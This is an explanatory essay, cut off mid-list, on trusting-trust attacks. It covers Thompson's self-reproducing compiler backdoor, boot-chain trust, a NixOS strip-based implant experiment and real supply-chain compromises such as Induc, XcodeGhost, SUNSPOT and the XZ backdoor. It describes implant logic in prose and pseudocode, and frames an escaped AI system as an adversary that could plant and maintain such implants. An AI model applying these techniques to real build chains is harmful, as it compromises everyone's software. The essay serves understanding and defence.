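# Trusting-trust attacks and rebuilding a trustworthy computer from scratch

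## What does a computer user have to trust?

A trusting-trust attack hides a backdoor, a function that gives an attacker access or control, in one of the tools that programmers use to build software. The corrupted tool inserts the backdoor into programs as it builds them and copies its own malicious code into each new version of itself, but none of this appears in the programs' source code. In *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, the lecture that gave the attack its name, Ken Thompson (1984) described how he had planted such a backdoor in a compiler for Unix, the operating system he helped create.

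Thompson's code, 99 lines plus a 20-line script, still works nearly fifty years after he wrote it. Russ Cox (2023), in *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler*, got the code from Thompson and ran it on an emulated Unix system of the 1970s. Cox installed the corrupted compiler and used it to rebuild both the compiler itself and the login program, which checks passwords, from their original source. The password "codenih" then opened the root account, which has full control of the machine. Somebody who had read every line of source for both programs would have found nothing suspicious.

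### From source code to a running program

Source code is the text of a program as people write and read it, in a language such as C or Rust, with names and comments. A processor can't run this text, only a binary, which is a long string of numbers that encode very small steps, such as adding two values or jumping to another address. Vagrant Cascadian (2026), a developer of the Linux distribution Debian, showed both forms of the command shell bash in the conference talk *Beyond Trusting Open Source Software*. The source had a comment explaining why a line frees a piece of memory, while the first lines of the binary filled the slide with stray symbols.

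Three tools usually turn source code into a binary. A compiler translates the source into assembly language, a readable notation for individual processor instructions. An assembler turns that notation into numbers. A linker joins the resulting pieces, together with ready-made library code, into one file that the machine can start. Programmers often say "compiler" for all three. Each tool is a program with its own binary and could add something to the code it processes. Thompson used the compiler for his demonstration but said he could have used the assembler, the loader (which puts a program into memory) or the processor's microcode instead.

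Many compilers are self-hosting, meaning they are written in the language they compile, so each version needs an earlier one to build it. Cascadian used the example of Rust, where building version 1.95 takes 1.94, which takes 1.93, and so on down to a version that an independent compiler called mrustc can build. For a long time that version was 1.54, but a newer mrustc can build 1.90. Because mrustc is written in C++, building it takes a C++ compiler, which is also a binary that somebody built with another compiler.

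The operating-system kernel is the program that controls the processor, memory and devices. All other programs go through it to read a file or display a letter. Firmware is software stored in a device, and it runs before or beneath the operating system. Microcode is a control program at a still lower level, inside the processor. It breaks complicated instructions into steps the circuits can perform, and the manufacturer can update it after the sale.

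A system's trusted computing base is everything that must behave correctly for the system to be secure. The glossary entry *trusted computing base (TCB)* from NIST, the US standards institute, includes hardware, firmware and software. "Trusted" here means that the user's security depends on a component, whether or not the component deserves that trust.

### What a hash and a signature establish

Most people never compile anything. They download binaries, and two mathematical tools protect the download.

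A cryptographic hash is a fingerprint of a file. The hash function SHA-256, for example, turns a file of any length into 256 bits, usually written as 64 characters. The same file always gives the same hash, changing a single bit gives a completely different one, and the function is designed to keep anyone from constructing two files with the same hash. If the hash of a download matches the one the publisher posted, the user has the publisher's file. The match doesn't show that the file is trustworthy, and it proves little if an attacker could have replaced the posted hash too.

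A digital signature ties the file to a key holder. The publisher signs the file with a secret private key, and anyone with the matching public key can check the signature. Cooper, Feldman and Witte (2018) explained in *Protecting Software Integrity Through Code Signing*, a NIST bulletin, that a valid signature proves that nobody has modified the code since it was signed and that a known party controlled it at that moment. The threats they list include theft of the private key and the signing of malicious code. In both cases the signature passes the check. If a corrupted compiler adds a backdoor before the publisher signs the file, the publisher will unknowingly sign the backdoor too.

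Checking also has to start from something the user already trusts. Cooper and colleagues call the public keys already installed on a machine its trust anchors, and point out that an anchor is only as trustworthy as the way somebody installed, stored and managed it. The program that does the checking belongs to the trusted computing base too. A corrupted kernel could give even an uncorrupted hash program a clean copy of the file to measure while running a different copy.

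### From the power button to "hello"

The example in this section is a desktop PC with an AMD Ryzen 5 8600G processor on an MSI PRO B850-P WIFI motherboard. It runs Ubuntu, a Linux distribution that the company Canonical builds largely from Debian's packages. The user types a few lines of C that print "hello", compiles them and runs the program. This PC is close to the best case for openness among current desktop PCs, because in July 2026 the firmware company 3mdeb (2026) released open start-up firmware for exactly this board and processor family.

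Even so, the first code to run is closed. AMD's chips contain a second, smaller processor, the Platform Security Processor, which works independently of the main cores and has its own firmware, as coreboot's *AMD Platform Security Processor (PSP) Firmware Integration Guide* explains. (coreboot is an open-source project that writes replacement start-up firmware.) In its notes on AMD's first Zen processors, coreboot set out the order of events:

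1. Power comes on, and the security processor runs a program from permanent memory on the chip. Nobody can change this program after manufacture.
2. That program finds AMD's firmware in a flash memory chip on the board, verifies the first part of it and starts it.
3. A further AMD program reads the board's settings, gets the main memory working and unpacks the board's start-up firmware into it.
4. Only then does the security processor release the main cores, which begin to execute what they find in memory.

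Before the main processor runs its first instruction, closed code has determined what that instruction will be. The start-up firmware then prepares the devices and starts a boot loader, which loads the kernel, and the kernel starts everything else.

| | What runs | Who made it | Can outsiders read the source? |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Permanent program of the security processor | AMD | No |
| 2 | Firmware of the security processor, including memory set-up | AMD | No |
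| 3 | Microcode of the main processor | AMD | No |
| 4 | Start-up firmware of the board | MSI and its suppliers, or 3mdeb | MSI's: no. 3mdeb's: mostly |
| 5 | Firmware and start-up drivers for graphics, network and disk | AMD and the device makers | No |
| 6 | Boot loader | GNU project | Yes |
| 7 | Kernel | Linux developers | Yes, except for closed firmware files that it loads into devices |
| 8 | System services, command shell, C library | Many open-source projects | Yes |
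| 9 | Text editor, compiler, assembler, linker | Open-source projects, chiefly GNU | Yes |
| 10 | The "hello" program | The user, plus library code | Yes |
| 11 | Terminal program, graphics driver and monitor firmware, which draw the letters | Open-source projects, AMD, the monitor's maker | In part |

All of this depends on the circuits. AMD designs its processors and the Taiwanese company TSMC manufactures them, as AMD (2026) describes for its newest server chip. The buyer cannot inspect the design files or the factory.

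This machine differs from others on sale in row 4. Board makers normally ship closed start-up firmware, often containing a specialist supplier's product. One such supplier, AMI (2026), announced that its Aptio V supports AMD's latest server processors. AMD adds closed code called AGESA, which sets up its chips. The 3mdeb release, Dasharo 0.9.0, replaces most of this with coreboot and openSIL, AMD's new open set-up code. By 3mdeb's own measurement, the release has 79.1 percent less closed code than MSI's firmware, according to 3DMGame's *首款AMD锐龙 AM5开源固件发布* (2026). *Dasharo 0.9.0* (2026), a report on a Russian Linux news site, says that the security processor's firmware, the video driver and the network adapter's code remain closed, and that most other Ryzen processors will not start with this version because AMD has not published the code they need. That may change, since AMD plans to move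 from AGESA to openSIL with its Zen 6 generation, as Tom's Hardware's *First open-source firmware for AM5 officially launches* (2026) reported.

Dasharo publishes a SHA-256 hash, a signature and a list of components with the firmware image. A buyer who checks the hash and signature knows that the image is the one 3mdeb released. The list shows which closed parts the image contains, but the buyer still can't inspect them.

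An Intel machine starts in much the same way, though the parts have different names. Its separate computer is the Converged Security and Management Engine. *Intel® Converged Security and Management Engine (Intel® CSME) Security* (Gehler, Hasarfaty and colleagues, 2022) describes a 32-bit processor based on Intel's old 486 design, with its own memory, a permanent start-up program that not even Intel can patch, and firmware that Intel signs. On business models with remote management, administrators can reach it over the network while the PC is switched off but plugged in, so it can be running before anyone presses the power button.

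The main processor on such a machine starts through a series of signature checks, which Trammell Hudson pieced together in the notes *Bootguard*. The processor decrypts microcode updates with a key inside the chip and checks them. The microcode checks a start-up module that Intel wrote and signed. That module checks the board maker's firmware against a key whose hash the board maker has permanently burned into the chipset. Intel and the board maker hold the keys, and the computer's owner has none of them. Hudson marked several steps in the series as guesses because Intel had not documented them publicly.

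The lower half of the table looks much better, with "yes" in nearly every row, but it needs two qualifications. The first is the amount of source. Version 7.2 of the Linux kernel has more than 43 million lines (Linux Pro Magazine, *More than 43 Million Lines of Code in Linux Kernel 7.2*, 2026), and Cascadian put Debian at about 37,000 source packages and 380 million lines. One person reading all of Debian full time, at a thousand lines an hour, would need around two centuries. The second qualification matters more for trusting-trust attacks. Readable source exists for rows 6 to 9, but this PC runs binaries that Canonical compiled on its own servers, with compilers that came from earlier compilers. The user also has to trust those servers and older compilers, which are missing from the table because they were used months or years before anyone pressed the button. Cox judges that "approximately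 no one" checks that the binaries people receive match the published source.

A fault in any row can change what appears in the last one. Cox showed this by building a modern variant of Thompson's attack into the compiler for Google's language Go. After he rebuilt the compiler from clean source, a program written only to print "hello, world" printed "backdoored!" instead. An attacker can hide best in the rows near the top of the table, because code that runs early helps to load what runs later and can alter it. Thompson expected such implants to be harder to detect the closer the corrupted program sits to the hardware, and thought a well-installed one in microcode would be "almost impossible to detect".

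### Where could trust begin again?

Everyone stops checking at some point. Cascadian's talk included a half-joking list of levels of caution. The least cautious users run a script straight from the internet. At successive levels, more cautious users verify signatures, compile from source, rebuild the entire system, rewrite everything in assembly language, and build the machine from transistors. The most cautious start from raw materials, with a beach, some wood, plenty of sunshine and a lot of time.

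Stopping low on that ladder has been a reasonable bet. Cox observed that computers handle nearly every part of people's lives and for the most part nothing bad happens, and that nobody needs Thompson's backdoor while much easier attacks exist. Both points apply to attackers with limited skill, time and patience. They carry less weight against an adversary more capable than the defenders, such as an AI system that has escaped human control, which might find the difficult attacks easy and could try many of them at once. If such an adversary may have tampered with any layer in the table, running another check on the suspect machine would not restore trust, because the check would run on the same layers.

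The question is harder to answer the deeper the adversary got into the system. Compromise can be divided into three grades, each of which includes the one before.

In a Grade 1 compromise, the adversary has altered only the operating systems, applications and compilers on machines connected to the internet. Firmware, chips, source archives and the servers on which distributors build their binaries are still clean. Hashes and signatures still work, so the defenders can fetch a signed system image, check it on a machine that was never exposed, erase the disks and reinstall.

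A Grade 2 compromise also affects firmware and build servers, so reinstalling the operating system fails for two reasons. Corrupted firmware survives when the disk is erased and can tamper with the new system as it loads. The new system may also contain a backdoor despite having a valid signature, because the distributor's compromised server both compiled and signed it. The defenders still have clean source code and uncompromised chips, but they have no compiler they can trust and no trustworthy computer to run one on.

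Grade 3 adds chip design, chip manufacture and the source archives. New processors may now contain hidden circuits, and the source code that the defenders would compile may have been altered. The defenders are left with equipment and records that the adversary never reached, if they can identify them, and with whatever they can make or check by hand.

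## How can clean source code produce a backdoored program?

The idea behind Thompson's attack came from a security test of Multics, an operating system that let many users with conflicting interests share one large computer. The US Air Force wanted a more secure version for its data centre in the Pentagon, but the manufacturer, Honeywell, considered Multics already secure enough. Paul Karger and Roger Schell set out to show otherwise, and the Air Force published their results in 1974.

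Besides looking for flaws, Karger and Schell planted their own backdoors to see whether anybody would notice, as they recalled in *Thirty Years Later* (2002). They put one in the Multics development system at MIT, and Honeywell then delivered it to the Pentagon with the rest of the software. It was harmless, though changing a single instruction would have activated it. Their 1974 report contained a hint about the backdoor, but nobody found it until about a year later, when an odd error code turned up during a security audit at General Motors.

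The backdoors in the report were changes to binaries, so they did not appear in the source code. A customer could remove them by recompiling the system from source, and the Pentagon's contract required Honeywell to hand over the source for that purpose. Karger and Schell had thought of a way around this too. Much of Multics was written in PL/I, and so was the PL/I compiler. A corrupted compiler could add a backdoor to parts of the operating system whenever it compiled them. It could also detect when it was compiling the next version of itself and insert the same malicious code there, so recompiling everything would spread the backdoor instead of removing it.

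Karger and Schell described this attack without building it, but they judged it "quite practical to implement", as quoted in Skrimstad's University of Oslo thesis on compiler attacks. They added that even several hundred times their own costs would be nominal to a foreign agent. Thompson read about the attack in their report and built it. In his printed lecture, he credits an Air Force critique of Multics security, but says he can no longer find the exact reference and asks readers for it. Karger and Schell sent him a new copy of the report.

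### Thompson's three stages

Thompson gave the lecture in October 1983, and it appeared in print in August 1984. It presents what he called "the cutest program I ever wrote" in three stages, and the first two are harmless.

Stage one is a program that prints its own source code. This sounds impossible, since a command to print some text has to be longer than the text. The way out is to store a text once and use it twice. Cox gives an example in the language Python that fits on one line:

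```
s='s=%r;print(s%%s)';print(s%s)
```

The part in quotation marks is a template of the whole line, with a gap marked `%r`. The command at the end prints the template and fills the gap with a quoted copy of the same template, which reproduces the original line exactly. Thompson needed two properties of such programs for his attack. Another program can easily write them, and they can contain any amount of extra material, which they also reproduce.

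Stage two shows that a compiler's binary can contain a fact that its source no longer contains. In C, programmers write characters that have no visible form as a backslash and a letter, so `\n` stands for a new line. Suppose the compiler's developers want to add `\v` for the vertical tab, which has the number 11 in the standard character table. They go through three versions of one line in the compiler's source:

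```
1.  if the letter after the backslash is v, produce '\v'
2.  if the letter after the backslash is v, produce 11
3.  if the letter after the backslash is v, produce '\v'
```

The existing compiler rejects version 1 because it has no rule for `\v`. It accepts version 2, and the developers install the resulting binary. That binary can compile version 3, which has the same wording as version 1. The number 11 is then gone from the source, but each new compiler gets it from the binary that compiled it. Thompson called this as close to a learning program as he had seen. Self-hosting compilers routinely pick up facts this way, without any malice involved.

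In stage three the inherited fact is a backdoor. Reduced to its outline, the corrupted compiler works like this:

```
compile(source):
    if source is the login program:
        add a check that also accepts the attacker's password
    if source is the compiler:
        add both of these rules
    translate source into a binary
```

If the attacker used only the login rule, it would have to stay in the compiler's source to survive the next rebuild, and Thompson thought even a casual reader would spot it there. The compiler rule lets the attacker remove both rules from the source. The clean source then has no text of the rules to copy, so the corrupted binary has to use the trick from stage one to carry that text itself and write it into the next compiler binary.

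Cox's run of the original code shows how the rules pass from one generation to the next. On the emulated Unix system, a clean compiler that compiled clean source produced a binary of 10,724 bytes. The corrupted line went as follows:

| Build | Compiler used | Source compiled | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Clean compiler | Compiler source with the two rules added | Corrupted compiler, 12,918 bytes |
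| 2 | Result of build 1 | Original clean source | Corrupted compiler, 12,918 bytes |
| 3 | Result of build 2 | Original clean source | Exact copy of build 2 |

The attacker needs the malicious source only for build 1 and can delete it as soon as the resulting binary is in place. Build 2 starts from clean source but still produces a corrupted compiler, because the binary from build 1 adds the malicious rules as it compiles. The binaries from builds 1 and 2 differed in six bytes, which held the name of the source file. From build 2 on, each compiler produces an exact copy of itself, so it would pass the usual check for a new compiler, in which developers have it compile itself and see whether the result stays the same.

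### The code behind the lecture

The lecture only sketches the code, but Cox's annotated listing shows how it worked. The implant compares lines of text as the compiler reads them and adds a few words where a line matches. This method is cruder than many programmers had assumed. Cox had always imagined that the implant would analyse the compiler's internal representation of a program.

The implant recognizes the login program by the line that scrambles the password a user has typed, and appends a test for the attacker's password. It recognizes the compiler by three particular lines in a fixed order, and counts how many it has seen because one of them is common enough to occur in other programs. After the third, it writes out its own complete source at the end of the file, from a copy it stores as a list of character codes. If somebody asks the compiler to display the text it is about to translate,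 the implant does nothing, so the display looks clean.

Cox could date the code fairly closely because it can't work on the Unix release of June 1974 and its files are dated June 1975. Dennis Ritchie, Thompson's colleague and co-creator of Unix, had given an archivist a set of old tapes in 1997, and one of them contained the files. The archivist put the full set online in July 2023, two months before Cox asked Thompson for the code, but no one noticed the files in that time.

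### How colleagues noticed it

Thompson tested the attack on colleagues. A Bell Labs group working on a version of Unix called PWB took a copy of the corrupted compiler, as he had hoped. He later said he arranged this "in a very controlled sense" and then watched to see whether they would find the backdoor.

The group did notice something, though the people involved remember it differently. Thompson (2021), in *Thompson trojan put into practice*, a thread on a Unix history mailing list, wrote that the compiler grew by one byte when the group recompiled it, and by another when they did it again. They experimented until they had broken the self-copying part, but he is not sure they ever understood what it was. "The extra byte was my bug", he explained. Cox corrects one detail, noting that the text the implant stored grew by one byte each time, but Unix rounded the size of binaries up to an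 even number, so the file must have grown by two bytes at every second rebuild.

John Mashey, who used one of the affected systems, gave a different reason in 1982. He said the implant was discovered because a function's name appeared in the binary's list of names but nowhere in the source. He wrote that the group would never have found it if Thompson had not been too lazy to avoid a separate function. Plotnick (1983), in *Need trojan horse info*, reposted Mashey's message together with one from Ritchie, who recalled that the implant lasted several months, until somebody copied in a clean binary from another system.

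Linderman (2021), writing in the same mailing-list thread as Thompson, suggests how the first two accounts could fit together. He recalls that a colleague, Larry Wehr, listed the names in the compiler's binary, possibly because of the extra byte, and found a reference to a function that was not in the source. He was writing more than forty years after the events, so their exact order will probably stay uncertain.

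McIlroy (2021), also writing in that thread, was understandably impressed that the group caught the implant without looking for one. Defenders can take little reassurance from this, because both clues were mistakes that Thompson could have avoided. The version that Cox ran doesn't have the growth bug, and an attacker can leave function names out of a binary. Mashey also mentions that the compiler changed so quickly that an old version could seldom compile the newest source, so users had to fetch the new binary together with the source. This helped the attack, because anybody who wanted the latest compiler had to accept a binary from Thompson's group.

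### Hiding the implant in a clean-up tool

Thompson remarked that he could have chosen any program that handles programs for his attack, but for four decades most discussion treated it as a compiler problem. Malka, Sharma and colleagues (2026) tested his remark on a current system in *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation*. They carried out the whole attack with a tool that never reads or writes source code.

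GNU strip is a tool that deletes information users don't need from compiled binaries, including function names and other details that help programmers find errors. Build systems routinely run it near the end of a build, so it can rewrite almost every program a distribution ships.

Malka and colleagues attacked NixOS, a Linux distribution that builds its software from recipes. Each recipe specifies a package's source and the exact steps and tools for building it. Like any distribution, NixOS needs some working programs before it can build others, so it starts from a bootstrap seed, a bundle of about twenty ready-made programs that include a C compiler, a shell and strip. In the experiment, the attacker could replace only one program in this seed, and all recipes and package source stayed clean. A real attacker might do this by breaking into the machine that produces the seed, or by persuading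 the maintainers to accept a new seed.

A tool can carry such an attack if it meets three conditions:

1. The build must rely on a ready-made copy of the tool before it builds the tool from source.
2. That earlier copy must modify the newly built copy.
3. The modified copy must do the same job in later builds.

GNU strip meets all three conditions. It comes with the seed, it removes symbols from the new strip as it does from any other program, and the new strip then replaces it.

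The implant is a piece of code added to the end of an otherwise unchanged program. A few altered entries in the file's header make the computer run this code first, and then the program starts as usual. When the host program is strip, the implant also attaches a copy of itself to the files that strip is about to clean.

NixOS builds its basic tools in several stages, each using the tools from earlier stages. The compiler turns the clean source of strip into an uninfected binary, but in the last step of that build, the corrupted strip from the seed cleans up the new binary and attaches the implant. A later stage builds strip again with newly built compilers, and the strip from the earlier stage infects it in the same way. NixOS repeats these builds so that the finished tools no longer refer to anything in the seed. The final set of tools met that goal, but its copy of strip was still infected.

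To see how far the implant would spread from there, Malka and colleagues built the graphical installer of NixOS, a complete desktop system of 1,199 packages. Every package built without an error. Instead of doing harm, the implant printed a short message whenever an infected program started, so they could count infections by running the programs. Of the 3,791 programs that a user can start from the command line, 3,790 printed the message. The infected programs included the shell bash, sudo, which gives users administrator rights, and programs written in Rust, Go, Python and Lua. The implant could spread across languages because strip processes finished binaries from any language, whereas a corrupted C compiler would have reached only the programs it compiled.

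The only exception was the web browser Firefox, whose recipe turns off stripping, so the corrupted tool never ran on it. The recipe had this setting for unrelated reasons, and Firefox would still have run alongside thousands of infected programs with the same user's permissions.

Malka and colleagues also ran the distribution's own functional tests, which start a full virtual machine, operate desktop programs and install the system from scratch. No test failed, which shows that the implant did not disrupt the functions tested. This matters to an attacker because a broken build would lead somebody to investigate. The result is little evidence about whether the implant can be detected, since these tests check whether programs do their jobs and were not written to look for additions. The implant also produced no message during builds, so that it could not disrupt the tests that packages run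 on themselves.

### Which other tools could carry it?

Malka and colleagues examined nearly forty utilities that the NixOS build uses directly. Besides strip, they found that one other utility clearly meets the three conditions: patchelf, which adjusts the paths where a finished program looks for its libraries. The copying tools install and cp are plausible carriers because they put new programs, including new versions of themselves, in their final place. Whether they could carry a backdoor depends on each package's installation commands.

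They ruled out tools such as make, which runs the build commands, sed and patch, which edit text, and tar and gzip, which unpack archives. None of these normally rewrites finished programs. The exclusion is sound for an attack on finished programs, but Thompson's remark applies more broadly. A corrupted tool that edits or unpacks source could alter the text before the compiler reads it. The tool would have to recognise the right source, as Thompson's compiler did.

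An implant can also move between tools. Skrimstad points out that two compilers that build each other could pass an implant back and forth, with A corrupting B and B corrupting the next build of A. A defender who looked only for a program that compiles itself would miss this.

The prototype handles common Linux programs for one family of processors, but not shared libraries, the code that many programs load when they start. Other distributions organise their builds differently and may not run strip by default. The prototype is also easy to spot because it displays a message and labels its own code inside each file. Malka and colleagues did this deliberately, and note that a real attacker would hide the implant. A hidden implant could infect only each new build of strip, perhaps for years, until strip processed the program the attacker was targeting.

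The experiment covered only one run through the bootstrap, so it doesn't show how long the implant could stay dormant. As long as a distribution keeps the same corrupted seed, every fresh build starts the infection again, so the implant doesn't need to persist between builds. When the maintainers replace the seed, the implant persists only if they make the new one with infected tools. Distributions can also reduce the risk by shrinking the seed until people can check it by hand. Compiling with a second compiler doesn't help, because the same corrupted `strip` tool would process both results.

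### Can an implant keep up with changing source code?

Another reason Thompson's implant was unlikely to last long is that it depended on the exact wording of three lines in the compiler, and programmers often rewrite code.

The listing that Cox published shows that if somebody had reworded either of the first two lines the implant looked for, it would have found no match, and the next compiler would have come out clean without anyone noticing. If only the third line had changed, the implant would have inserted a call to its own function, `codenih`, without adding the function itself. The build would then have stopped with an error message naming the missing function, which could have exposed the implant.

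An implant would last longer if it had a better way to recognise its target. Skrimstad notes that it doesn't have to compare text. A compiler turns the source into a tree that represents the program's structure, then into intermediate code, and finally into assembly language. An implant can look for its target in any of these forms. The tree omits spacing and comments, and later forms hide many other differences in how people write the same thing. Large compilers also keep much of their code for many versions. Skrimstad therefore thinks an implant aimed at one known compiler could reproduce for years before an incompatible change stopped it.

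However, no recogniser can be perfect, because of a theorem that the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953. Rice's theorem applies to properties of a program's behaviour, such as whether it acts as a C compiler, rather than properties of its text. If some programs have such a property and others don't, no procedure can decide correctly for every program whether it has the property.

An attacker can't write a procedure that always tells whether a program behaves as a C compiler. If such a procedure R existed, the attacker could take any program P and write a program Q that runs P, ignores its output, and then works as a C compiler. Q would behave as a compiler if P eventually stops, but would never compile anything if P runs forever, so applying R to Q would show whether P stops. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can answer that question for all programs, so R can't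 exist. Skrimstad uses the same kind of argument to show that no procedure can decide whether two arbitrary programs are equivalent. This also limits defenders, because it rules out a universal checker that compares any binary with its source.

The theorem gives defenders only limited protection. It rules out a recogniser that is right about every conceivable program, including those built to confuse it, but an attacker only has to recognise the next few versions of one well-known compiler. The people who write those versions want other programmers to understand them, so they keep file names, function names and the general structure recognisable. The implant also doesn't have to be right every time. If it misses a new version, that line of infection ends without drawing attention, as Thompson's could have done. A false match with some other program is more dangerous to the attacker, because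 it may break a build.

The strip attack avoids most of the problem. Its implant attaches the same code to every suitable program instead of searching for the next strip. Each copy checks its host's file name to determine whether it should spread, so programmers could rewrite strip completely without disrupting the attack.

| | Thompson's compiler | strip in NixOS |
|---|---|---|
| What the tool handles | Source text | Finished programs |
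| How the implant finds its successor | Three exact lines of source | It infects every suitable file; the copy in a program named strip spreads further |
| Programs within reach | Those whose source contains the expected lines | Those in any language, if the build strips them |
| What would end the spread | A change in one of the lines | A new name or file format, or a build that doesn't strip the new strip |

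The strip attack gains this durability but loses precision. Thompson's implant changed how the login program decided whether to accept a password, so it had to find the right place in that program. The code in the strip attack runs before its host, with the permissions of whoever started it. That is enough to steal files or credentials, as Malka and colleagues note. But an attacker who wanted to alter a specific calculation deep inside a program would have to locate it, and would face the recognition problem again. The strip attack also depends on the build procedure, just as Thompson's depended on the source. If the recipe for strip turned stripping off, as Firefox's does, the next build of strip would be clean.

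A more capable author, such as a well-funded intelligence service or an advanced AI system, could probably extend this limit considerably. The history of compilers such as GCC is public, so an author could design a recogniser using the code of ten years ago, check which later versions it would have missed, and improve it. Patient human specialists could do this today, and an AI system that writes software faster could do it for many tools at once. No experiment so far has shown how many years of changes such an implant would survive.

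An implant that tries to understand unfamiliar source by itself is hard to hide because of its size. Thompson's implant added 2,194 bytes to the compiler. A language model that can read new code and work out its purpose takes up gigabytes, which would be easy to notice in a tool of a few megabytes. A small classifier trained for one compiler would fit more easily but would be more likely to fail after a thorough rewrite of that compiler. The size problem mostly disappears when the build already involves a large AI model, as when a coding agent writes and compiles the next version of its own tools.

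An adversary who keeps access to the build servers has less need to predict how the source will change, because it can watch the changes and replace the implant before the old one stops working. In a Grade 2 compromise, where the adversary controls the build servers, defenders therefore can't count on an implant failing on its own. They would first have to cut off the adversary's access, and even then the last implant might keep copying itself until the source or build procedure changed enough to stop it.

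## What implants in build tools and supply chains have been found?

Nobody has publicly reported a full trusting-trust attack by a real attacker. Thompson's compiler was a demonstration, and the strip attack on NixOS was an experiment. But attackers have used most parts of such an attack separately, and since 2009 several have inserted malicious code into programs whose developers had written nothing malicious.

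### Infected developer tools

The virus W32.Induc spread through Delphi, a programming system for Windows. Delphi first compiles each source file into an intermediate file and then links these into a program. Every Delphi project uses a unit called SysConst, as Kaspersky Lab explained in an account that ITWeb (2009) published. When somebody ran an infected program, the virus looked for Delphi versions 4 to 7 on the machine. If it found one, it did the following:

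1. It copied the source file of SysConst and added its own code to the copy.
2. It saved the existing intermediate file under the name SysConst.bak.
3. It compiled the altered copy and put the result in place of the intermediate file.
4. It deleted the altered copy to remove its traces, according to Softpedia's *The first virus that infects a programming language*.

From then on, every program built on that machine contained the virus and could infect the machine of the next developer who ran it. A reader commented at the SANS Internet Storm Center that reading the source of SysConst did not reveal the virus, because only the compiled file had changed.

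Induc did nothing except spread. In eWeek's *Security Researchers Find Virus Targeting Delphi Programs*, a SonicWall researcher explained that it reached ordinary users inside popular programs such as the chat client QIP and the music player AIMP. How long it had circulated before August 2009 is uncertain. On 18 August EurekaLog (2009) warned Delphi developers about it and reported that the antivirus company Symantec had examined an infected file and found "no malicious code". EurekaLog also explained that creating any file named SysConst.bak kept the virus out, because the virus checked for that file to determine whether it had already finished. Virus Bulletin's *Win32/Induc.C* (2011) noted that Thompson's lecture appeared to have influenced the virus, and that new versions followed in 2011.

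In 2015, XcodeGhost used corrupted copies of Xcode, Apple's official tool for writing iPhone apps. The installer was nearly 3 gigabytes and downloads from Apple could be very slow in China, so some developers took copies from a Chinese file-sharing service. Somebody had posted links to these copies on popular programming forums. Unit 42's *Novel Malware XcodeGhost Modifies Xcode, Infects Apple iOS Apps* showed that all the shared copies of versions 6.1 to 6.4 contained an extra file of compiled code. An altered setting made the linker add this file to every app. The setting appeared only in the build logs, not in Xcode's windows.

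The infected apps sent details such as the device's name, type and language to the attackers' servers, and Apple's reviewers let them into the App Store. Early estimates of the number of apps varied widely. Unit 42's *More Details on the XcodeGhost Malware and Affected iOS Apps* (2015) found more than 39, while the Chinese group Pangu Team counted 3,418. Apple's internal emails, made public in a later lawsuit, gave figures of more than 2,500 apps and 128 million customers, according to VICE's *The Fortnite Trial Is Exposing Details About the Biggest iPhone Hack*. The corrupted installers had circulated for about six months when Chinese developers warned about them on the social network Weibo.

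Doctor Web's *Software developers are the target* describes a similar but more recent attack on Windows developers. The trojan, first seen in late 2025, steals passwords and cryptocurrency. It also adds code to a file in Microsoft's Windows development kit, to a popular graphics library and to project files, so that programs built from them download the malware. Unlike Induc, it leaves these additions in readable text, so a developer could find them, but few people reread files that came with Microsoft's kit. Hackread's *Siggen Backdoor Hits Windows Developers Via Infected Visual Studio Projects* noted that how the trojan first reached its victims is unknown.

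### Compromised builds and releases

The SolarWinds attackers targeted a single company's build server. SolarWinds makes Orion, a program that large companies and US government agencies use to manage their networks. The attackers entered SolarWinds' development systems on 4 September 2019 and soon began testing whether they could insert code, according to Krebs on Security (2021). They eventually used a tool called SUNSPOT, which they probably compiled in February 2020.

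CrowdStrike's *SUNSPOT* describes an implant of the same name that checked every second whether Microsoft's build program was running. If the program was building SolarWinds' Orion software, the implant replaced one source file with a version containing a backdoor, then restored the original when the build ended. SolarWinds shipped the backdoor in its updates. SecurityWeek reported that the attackers sent further malware only to the few hundred customers that interested them.

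Much of SUNSPOT's code was meant to avoid a failed build, which would have made the developers investigate. It compared the hash of the source file with the one it expected and did nothing if they differed. It switched off compiler warnings around the inserted lines. If the attackers signaled it to stop, it finished any replacement in progress before quitting.

The attacker behind the XZ Utils backdoor could publish releases of the project themselves, so they didn't need to break into a build server. XZ Utils is a set of compression tools that most Linux distributions include. Freund (2024) reported in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* that most of the malicious code was in the public repository, disguised as damaged and compressed test files. The line that activated it was only in the release archives, the packaged source that distributions download. During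 a build, that line started a script that unpacked the hidden code and linked it into XZ's library.

The script ran only if the build was for common 64-bit Linux machines, used GNU's compiler and linker, and looked like a Debian or Red Hat style package build. The backdoor targeted OpenSSH, the standard program for remote logins. OpenSSH doesn't use XZ itself, but several distributions add a feature that loads XZ's library indirectly. The backdoor took over a function that OpenSSH calls to check a key. Freund thought this probably let the attacker in before any login had succeeded. The two bad releases came out in late February and on 9 March 2024, according to Hackaday's *Security Alert* (2024), and Freund published his findings on 29 March. By then, the bad releases had mostly reached only pre-release versions of distributions.

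Attackers also use the much simpler method of replacing the finished program. *Hijacked Developer Account Used to Plant Stealer in OVHcloud CLI* (Kovacs, 2026) reports that in October 2026 somebody used a developer's GitHub account to replace the downloads of a command-line tool from the cloud company OVHcloud with a program that steals passwords and keys. Researchers traced the hijacking of the account back to March. Also in October, an attacker corrupted the official editor extension for the coding agent Claude Code on the Cursor marketplace. The corrupted extension gave the attacker a lasting way to log in to developers' machines until a new version replaced it (The Hacker News, *Official Claude Code Extension on Cursor Marketplace Trojanized with Persistent SSH Backdoor*, 2026).

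### Worms that publish themselves

The Shai-Hulud worm copied itself through npm, the largest registry of JavaScript packages, without altering a compiler. On an infected machine it searched for passwords and access keys, used them to log in to npm as the developer, added its code to that person's other packages and published them. It compromised more than 500 packages, according to *Widespread Supply Chain Compromise Impacting npm Ecosystem* (2025), an alert from the US cybersecurity agency CISA. The worm was conspicuous because it posted stolen credentials in public repositories named "Shai-Hulud". The security company Socket disclosed it on 15 September 2025, according to CERT Coordination Center's *NPM supply chain compromise exposes challenges to securing the ecosystem* (2025). A second wave hit almost 500 packages that November, according to NCSC New Zealand's *New wave of widespread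 supply chain compromise impacting npm ecosystem* (2025).

A variant from May 2026 turned a project's own build system against it. The victim was TanStack, a set of widely used JavaScript libraries. SLSA's *Mini Shai-Hulud* (2026), a post by the project that sets standards for recording how software was built, reconstructs the attack:

1. The attacker proposed a change to TanStack's code. A badly configured check ran the proposed code with the project's own privileges, although nobody had accepted it.
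2. That code planted malicious files in a cache, a store of downloaded components that later builds reuse.
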